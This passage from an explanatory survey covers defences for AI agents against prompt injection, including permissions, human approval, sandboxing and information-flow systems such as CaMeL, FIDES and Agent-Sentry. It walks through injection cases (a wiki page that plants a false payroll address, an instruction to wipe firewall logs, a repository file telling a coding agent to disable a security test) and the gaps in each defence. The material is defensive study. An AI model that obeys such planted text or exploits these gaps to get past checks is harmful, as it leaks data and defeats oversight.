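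Their procurement example illustrates the reason for this caution. A company gives an agent wide access to its financial systems, email and contracts, and evaluates the permissions only at deployment. An attacker compromises a minor tool the agent uses, then exploits the agent's privileges to change contracts and approve payments. In the logs, the activity looks like a trusted agent doing its usual work, which delays detection.

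The guidance contains dozens of recommendations. Those that bear most directly on permission are:

- Give each agent its own cryptographic identity, and deny access to any agent or key that is missing from a trusted registry.
- Limit privileges to the minimum for the task, and issue credentials for high-impact actions only when the agent needs them.
- Verify identity and authorisation for every request at a central decision point.
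- Prevent agents from changing their own privileges, or from delegating without approval unless the delegation has an expiry time and a record of who granted it.
- Require human approval before high-impact actions. The system's designers or operators decide which actions these are, and the agent does not.
- Hold any request to delete logs until a person has reviewed it.

The last two would also stop the planted errand in the guidance's example. An insider outside the IT team asks an update agent to install a patch and "clean up the firewall logs", and the agent does both because it has permission to write anywhere on the system.

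The agencies report no tests of these measures and do not rank them by reliability. They list prompt-injection filters and a second agent that validates tasks alongside fixed controls, although NVIDIA's testers found model-based checks much easier to defeat. For decisions with moderate stakes, the guidance suggests approval by several agents, but they may all approve the false payroll address if they share a memory that contains it.

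### Human approval

Both the guidance and the Rule of Two rely on a person's approval when the stakes are high. How much this helps depends on whether people read what they approve. Anthropic's experiment with planted commands is evidence that people approve out of habit, since most testers let a clearly dangerous command through and rejections became rarer as the prompts accumulated. The high approval rate among Claude Code users is weaker evidence, because most of those commands were presumably harmless and a careful reader would have approved them too.

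The decline is a reason to ask the user less often. In Progent's AgentDojo runs, only 6 per cent of policy updates were expansions, so the solver would have spared the user the other 94 per cent of decisions. A long task with many updates could still produce several prompts. The perfect score under human review should also be interpreted with care, because Shi and colleagues simulated an alert reviewer who never granted unrestricted access to highly sensitive tools such as `send_money` and rejected any attempt to add a malicious address.

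Someone who reads an approval prompt carefully may still lack the facts needed to judge it. The developer in Choi and colleagues' attack approved a shell command because the prompt attributed it to the project's maintainer. A payroll clerk who sees "Send payroll file to `hr-reports@example.com`?" cannot tell that the address came from a page about laptops. The harness should build the prompt from the actual call and its own records rather than from the model's explanation. It could show that the address is new and where the chatbot found it. The clerk could then phone the contractor on a number the company already has.

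### Sandboxes and blocked connections

If a hijacked command gets past every check, the damage it can do depends on what the agent can reach. A sandbox, an isolated environment, restricts the files, programs and connections available to whatever runs inside it. OpenAI suggests judging a deployment by its "maximum completed effect", the most consequential outcome the agent can produce before another independent decision is required.

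OpenAI's example is a coding agent assigned to fix a bug in a private repository. A file there contains instructions to install an unapproved package and disable a security test. The repository's rules should block both changes. The agent has permission to propose a fix but not to merge it, and limits on outbound connections help contain the attempt. The agent may waste time or propose something harmful, but nothing reaches the company's live software without a separate decision.

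Outbound connections should have their own limit because an attacker needs a way to send stolen data out. NVIDIA recommends blocking them all by default, except to a short list of destinations that the agent's job requires. The agent must not be able to change that list. Where such controls were in place, NVIDIA's testers could not connect directly to the agent's machine and had to work through the agent, which made their attacks slower and less reliable. In the case of the AGENTS.md file in a customer's Downloads folder, such a block might have kept the session tokens from reaching the attacker even if the agent had collected them.

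The chat interface stayed open in NVIDIA's tests, and the testers obtained secrets through it. The payroll email would also get out, because it goes through the company's own mail server, which the chatbot needs for its work. A sandbox that permits this connection does not block bad emails while letting good ones through.

### When an allowed tool has an attacker's arguments

The clerk's request on day 22 satisfies all three limits as far as the tool can detect. She may send the payroll file, and the chatbot may send email. The task requires an email with that file attached, and only the address is wrong. Shi and colleagues say that Progent cannot defend against attacks that stay within the least privilege needed for the task, such as when an attacker persuades an agent to prefer his product over other valid options. They removed two AgentDojo attacks of this type, which steered the agent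 to a different legitimate hotel.

A condition on the recipient solves the problem when the company knows the right address beforehand. But an accounts department pays new suppliers every month, and their account numbers may exist only in documents that the agent has to read. A rule that lets the agent pay these suppliers also lets it pay an attacker's account, while limiting payments to accounts on file stops it from paying new suppliers at all.

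Some of Progent's successors therefore also check where an argument came from. In *ToolFence* (2026), an isolated model writes the policy from the user's request and tool descriptions that the operator has reviewed. The policy can require a sensitive argument to come from a specific field in a specific tool's result. For the cleaning firm's invoice, it could allow the amount to come from the invoice but require the account number to come from the company's supplier records. *ActGov* (2026) likewise distinguishes a value that the user supplied from the same value in an untrusted email. It classifies the source with a language model and then applies fixed rules, so a wrong classification can still lead to a wrong decision.

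*AgentCap* allows a payment that the user requested but rejects a recipient that appears only in a document the agent has read. It would also reject a new supplier's genuine account number until someone entered it in a record that the company trusts.

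## Checking where a command came from

The clerk's email on day 22 can pass checks on both form and permission, because nothing in the call shows that the recipient's address came from a page about laptops. To catch the false address, the harness needs information about its source.

*ToolFence* and *ActGov* check the sources of particular arguments. Information-flow control, an older technique from computer security, tracks the sources of all the data a program handles. The software labels each piece of data when it arrives, carries the labels over when the program combines data, and checks them before any sensitive action.

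### The labelling rule

In the simplest version, each value is either trusted (T) or untrusted (U). The user's request starts as T, and a web page or an outsider's email starts as U. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, define how labels combine. If a value v derives from v₁ to vₙ, then

label(v) = label(v₁) ⊔ … ⊔ label(vₙ)

where ⊔ picks the least trusted label. One untrusted ingredient makes the result untrusted, and copying, translating or summarising it does not change that. The rule also covers the model. Because nobody can reliably tell which part of the context shaped an output, everything the model writes takes the least trusted label in its context.

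Before a sensitive call, the harness looks at the label of the choice of tool, f, and the labels of the arguments, a₁ to aₙ. Under a strict policy, the call may run only if

label(f) ⊔ label(a₁) ⊔ … ⊔ label(aₙ) = T

The label of f matters because planted text could trigger a harmful action using only values the user supplied. A looser policy might require the label T for an email's recipient but accept U for its text, so that the agent can send a colleague a summary of a web page.

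Costa and colleagues also use a secrecy label, which lists the people who may read a value. Data derived from two documents may go only to people who may read both. If only the payroll office and the contractor may read the payroll file, the attacker's address fails this test even if the harness has wrongly labelled it as trusted.

Secrecy labels have to cover data that the agent is allowed to see. In *The Claws in Plain Sight*, Dong, Lu and colleagues (2026) gave five models a customer's profile and asked them to draft a product offer. Most sessions also included a planted memo claiming that a review required the personal details. In 40 of the 90 sessions where the prompt restricted use of the profile, the model copied at least one protected detail into its proposed call. The experiment captured the calls without sending them, so these were proposed disclosures rather than actual leaks.

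### Labelling the payroll email

In the original example, the employee's question is labelled trusted (T) and the wiki page untrusted (U). Once the page enters the context, everything the model proposes is also labelled U, including the call to `send_email`, so the harness refuses it. The chatbot can still answer the employee if the policy treats replies as harmless, as Costa and colleagues' policies do.

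The day 22 email requires finer labels, which the harness must have preserved through the summary and the shared memory:

| Part of the call | Derived from | Label |
|---|---|---|
| Choice of `send_email` | The clerk's request | T |
| Attachment | The clerk's request | T |
| Recipient | A memory note based on the wiki page | U |

The policy requires a trusted recipient, so the harness blocks the email. If the chatbot had taken the address from the company's supplier records, all three labels would be T and the email would go out.

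This table assumes that the false address has not affected the other two parts. If the memory note joins the clerk's words in the context, the whole call becomes U, and so does every later call in the conversation. An agent that worked this way could hardly send anything after reading a web page. Two designs from 2025 are meant to prevent this by keeping untrusted text away from the model that chooses the tools.

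### How CaMeL separates planning from reading

CaMeL, which researchers at Google DeepMind and ETH Zurich published in 2025, uses two models and an interpreter, an ordinary program that runs code line by line. It works in four steps:

1. A planning model receives the user's request, but no outside content, and writes the plan as a short program.
2. Where the plan needs information from outside text, a separate "quarantined" model reads the text and returns a value. This model has no tools.
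3. The interpreter runs the plan and tracks which sources each value depends on.
4. Before each tool call, the interpreter checks those sources against a policy.

For the payslip question, the plan might look like this, with illustrative names:

```
page   = search_wiki("check payslip on laptop")
answer = quarantined_model("How does she check it?", page)
reply(answer)
```

The hidden text can corrupt `answer`, so the employee may get bad advice. But it cannot add a line that exports the payroll file, because the planning model finished the program before anyone opened the page. On day 22, the program already contains a `send_email` line, so the protection comes from the policy, which rejects an address that depends on the wiki.

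*Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) reports that CaMeL achieved provable security on 77 per cent of the tasks its developers evaluated. The developers used the AgentDojo benchmark, and *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) reports that two injections still counted as successes there. In one, a document directed a payment, a case that CaMeL's developers place outside their threat model. In the other, the agent had only quoted hotel reviews, but AgentDojo's text matching wrongly counted the quotation as a successful attack.

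Other teams found that CaMeL completed fewer ordinary tasks. In *Agent-Sentry*, Sequeira, Damianakis and colleagues (2026) ran it on AgentDojo together with AgentDyn, a newer test with more open-ended tasks. CaMeL blocked 99.3 per cent of attacks but completed only 31.0 per cent of ordinary tasks, and took 26.6 seconds per run. In Choi and colleagues' tests, the strict version completed 36.5 per cent. The gap between these figures and 77 per cent is partly due to the choice of tasks, since AgentDyn's developers reported that CaMeL completed none of their open-ended ones.

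Without the policies, separating the models does not always stop attacks. In reruns for *The LLMbda Calculus* with policies switched off, 138 of 141 attacks in one category succeeded on one model. Two further attacks succeeded on a task that told the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The planning model had written a loop with a branch for every available tool, so instructions in the file could trigger any of them. Switching the policies on blocked every attack, but the agent completed far fewer tasks. By contrast, *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) reports that CaMeL resisted all 105 attacks on AgentDojo's Slack tasks even without policies. The protection that separation provides by itself seems to depend on how far the user's request lets outside text determine the agent's actions.

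The interpreter also has gaps. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026), which extends CaMeL to systems of several agents, explains that its tracking can miss influence that passes through a condition. Consider this fragment:

```
to = address_on_file
if page_announces_a_change:
    to = second_address_on_file
```

If the page contains no notice of a change, the interpreter skips the last line and `to` keeps its trusted label, even though the page determined which address it holds. Outside text can also steer a plan into one of its existing branches. The attacker can then choose only among actions the planning model wrote down, but a carelessly written plan may include a harmful one.

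### How FIDES hides untrusted text

In FIDES, which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, the main model works in the usual loop rather than fixing the whole plan in advance. When a tool returns a field less trusted than the current context, the harness stores the field under a name such as `#read_emails_0.body` and shows the model only the name. The model can pass the name to another tool, and the harness fills in the text when it makes the call. The context therefore stays trusted, while the stored value keeps its untrusted label.

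If a task requires understanding the hidden text, the main model can send a question to a quarantined model, whose answer goes into another named store. The main model can also read a stored value directly, but this makes the context untrusted, and the policy then blocks most sensitive calls.

The design includes a compromise for small answers, such as a yes or no from the quarantined model on whether any email asks for a meeting. A policy can let the main model act on that answer, because one bit is too short to carry an instruction. An attacker can still make the answer wrong, so this is safe only if neither answer leads to serious harm. Costa and colleagues did not test this feature.

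They ran AgentDojo with GPT-4o. After they removed misjudged cases, 152 injections had succeeded against an ordinary agent and 21 against FIDES with its policies off. None succeeded with the policies on, whether the agent used FIDES or one label for the whole context. The methods differed in how many tasks the agent completed when nobody was attacking it:

| AgentDojo environment | No policy, ordinary agent | Policy, one label for the context | Policy, FIDES | Tasks whose plan depends on data |
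|---|---|---|---|---|
| Office work | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% | 5.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% | 10.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% | 43.8% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% | 42.9% |

FIDES completed an average of 50 per cent of tasks across the four environments, compared with 42 per cent when the context had a single label and 84 per cent for the unprotected agent. Some of the loss comes from GPT-4o's trouble with named values, not from the policy. With o1, a stronger reasoning model, FIDES completed 68 per cent of the travel tasks, up from 41 per cent.

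The perfect security score may not carry over to a company's own systems, because Costa and colleagues labelled a field as untrusted if at least one AgentDojo attack used it. No attack in the test could therefore arrive through a field they had wrongly trusted. A company has no such list and must work out for itself which fields an outsider can write to. The test used a fixed set of attacks, but this matters less here than it would for a filter, because rewording an attack does not change the data's label. An adaptive attacker would have to look for a mislabelled source or a gap in the policy.

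### Paying an account number from an invoice

Suppose the bookkeeper asks the agent to pay a new supplier's first invoice. Her request determines the choice of tool, so that choice is trusted (T). The amount and the account number come from a PDF that an outsider wrote, so both are untrusted (U). She has let the invoice set the amount, and the policy can accept an untrusted amount below some limit. But the policy requires a trusted account number, so the harness blocks the payment, even though she asked for it and the company owes the money.

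A forged invoice would produce exactly the same labels as a genuine one. The labels correctly show that the number came from an outsider, but they can't show whether that outsider is the real supplier. *The LLMbda Calculus* reports that four independently built systems leave a similar set of cases unresolved, including payments directed by a document, and treats these as a limit of information-flow defences in general.

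Someone with authority can vouch for an untrusted value, which security researchers call endorsement. For example, if an agent takes the account number for a payment from an invoice, a bookkeeper can compare it with one she has obtained outside the agent, for instance by phone, and approve it. The harness then treats that account number as trusted for that payment. Checking the number against the same invoice would only confirm that the agent had copied it correctly.

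Dong and colleagues' design ties each confirmation to a digital fingerprint of the complete call, so changing any argument cancels the confirmation. They tried the design on only 12 synthetic sessions, enough to show that it runs but not how well it would protect a real agent.

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) describes recent work that reduces the number of such approvals by planning around untrusted data.

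### Agent-Sentry and the record of past runs

Most existing agents mix everything in one context and have no interpreter to track values. For these agents, a defender can try to infer a command's origin from what the agent does.

Agent-Sentry, a system Sequeira and colleagues released in March 2026, has the agent report where each argument in a tool call came from and whether it copied, derived or generated the value. The harness removes these notes before the call reaches the tool and assembles them into a graph that three checks use.

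A classifier compares the graph with records of earlier legitimate and hijacked runs. It uses 17 features, including the share of arguments from untrusted sources and whether a value appears word for word in untrusted text, to estimate the probability that the call is malicious. The system allows calls below 0.33 and blocks those at 0.66 or above. For calls in between, it accepts a sensitive value only if the value is on a list from earlier legitimate runs and also came from a trusted source. A language model judges the remaining cases, using the user's request and short excerpts of the outside text to decide whether each value came from ordinary content or from a passage containing instructions.

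| Test of Agent-Sentry | Legitimate runs allowed | Attacks blocked |
|---|---|---|
| Its own benchmark, learned classifier | 96.4% | 96.8% |
| AgentDojo and AgentDyn, same classifier with no training on them | 64.4% | 90.9% |
| AgentDojo and AgentDyn, handwritten detectors, unseen runs | 87.1% | 93.2% |
| AgentDojo and AgentDyn, handwritten detectors, runs used to build the rules | 95.1% | 94.3% |

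The results in the abstract come from the last row. Sequeira and colleagues defend that set-up as comparable to writing a policy with full knowledge of the tools, but the rows with unseen runs are a better guide to how the classifier would perform on new work. The classifier disrupted legitimate tasks most when the patterns were unfamiliar, especially in requests whose sensitive details were all in a file.

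It is also unclear how much security the graph adds. On Agent-Sentry's own benchmark, the judge alone allowed 98.0 per cent of legitimate runs and blocked 95.4 per cent of attacks, performing about as well as the full system. With an untuned prompt, those figures fell to 82.0 and 75.5 per cent. The graph's clearest benefits are speed and less reliance on a judge that attackers might manipulate, since only 3.1 per cent of decisions reached the judge.

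The model that the attacker is trying to mislead also writes the source notes. Agent-Sentry checks whether a value appears in the source the agent named, which catches simple false claims, but Sequeira and colleagues accept that this reduces the dependence on the model without removing it. They also say that the judge will not reliably stop an invoice that looks genuine but contains the attacker's account number. The false payroll address is a similar case, because the wiki page contains it as a stated fact, with no order to follow.

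### Finding the text that guided a call

Gao and colleagues' authority rule compares the provider of an instruction with the authority level a command requires, so they first need to find that instruction. Their August 2026 system, AttnLocate, searches for it using the model's attention weights, which determine how much each earlier token contributes to the next one.

The system averages these weights within each layer of the model and counts layers about two-thirds of the way through most heavily. It keeps only the attention from the final tool call to the outside content. A small neural network then marks the start and end of the passage that guided the call. The harness uses the markers in the context to look up who supplied that passage, then applies the authority rule.

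Some tokens attract strong attention whatever the model is doing. Gao and colleagues' detector wrongly flagged 41.7 per cent of legitimate calls in one set-up before they trained it to discount these tokens, and 5.6 per cent afterwards.

Across ten combinations of model and reasoning mode, the system detected 93.4 per cent of unauthorised calls and wrongly flagged 6.7 per cent of legitimate ones. The overlap between the passage it marked and the true one scored 0.743 on average, where 1 is a perfect match. At the company that runs 2,000 commands a day, the same false-alarm rate would produce about 130 false alarms daily.

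Detection also weakened as the context grew, from 97.2 per cent at up to 256 tokens to 85.7 per cent above 2,048. Agents routinely work with far longer contexts. The detector needs access to the model's internals, so it suits the model's developers and companies that host their own models. The detector also depends on correct markers. If a harness has moved the wiki text into a user message, AttnLocate can find the right passage and still attribute it to the user.

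### What tracking costs

An agent cannot plan some tasks, such as "Do what is on my to-do list", until it has read something. AgentDojo's banking tasks include several in which the user tells the agent to follow a file. FIDES fails many of these because reading the file makes the context untrusted and the policy then blocks the payment. This is by design, but users will think the agent does not work.

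Labels also tend to spread. If a model reads ten documents and uses one, a cautious harness gives its output the labels of all ten. *Sightline* (2026) calls the unnecessary labels "label creep" and tests methods that estimate which inputs flowed into a call. In its AgentDojo tests, its preferred method removed the most creep, let no attack call past a trust policy and kept the labels on almost all the inputs that attacks had used. But that is a measured rate, so a harness that drops labels based on such estimates gives up part of the guarantee that made labels attractive.

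Someone has to supply the labels for every tool. *APPA* (2026) lets a company add them gradually and treats unlabelled tools conservatively. This is safe but blocks more work until the labelling is complete.

Memory makes the problem worse. A summary of a long session usually draws on some untrusted text, so under the strict rule the whole summary is untrusted. If the harness drops that label, the text may return in a user message, which FIDES trusts by default. The harness therefore has to keep each note's label in its own storage, where the model cannot rewrite or omit it.

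A correct label can still mislead, because it records only where the text came from. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* warns that authentication establishes origin, not correctness, and should not automatically confer trust. If an attacker takes over a payroll clerk's account and changes the address in the supplier records, the chatbot's email carries trusted labels throughout. A company might also label its whole wiki as trusted because only staff can edit it. The altered laptop page would then pass every check in this section, although almost none of those staff have authority over payroll. Labels that list the possible writers would be more accurate than T and U, but someone would have to keep the lists up to date.

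### Use in products

By late 2026, at least one widely used agent had experimental support for information-flow control. Microsoft's undated post *Information-flow control* describes the feature in GitHub Copilot CLI, a command-line coding agent. Users have to switch it on. It keeps one label for the whole context and so far works only with selected tools from GitHub's own server.

In the post's example, a stranger opens an issue in a public repository and asks for information from a private one. GitHub's server can label the issue as untrusted and the private files as private. Once an agent's context contains both, the policy stops the agent from posting publicly. The policy doesn't interrupt an agent that works only with public repositories or only with private ones.

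GitHub's server supplies these labels only on request, and it labels everything in private repositories as trusted. That default is reasonable for a small team, but the server would also label a malicious file as trusted if a colleague had copied it in from elsewhere.

Developers who build their own agents can use Microsoft Agent Framework, whose security module hides untrusted results and sends questions about them to a quarantined model, much as FIDES does. When a call breaks the policy, the module can block it or ask a person. Microsoft has also released a gateway that adds labels to tools whose makers supply none. However, for each tool someone must describe its output, write a function that passes labels from arguments to results, and write or choose a policy.
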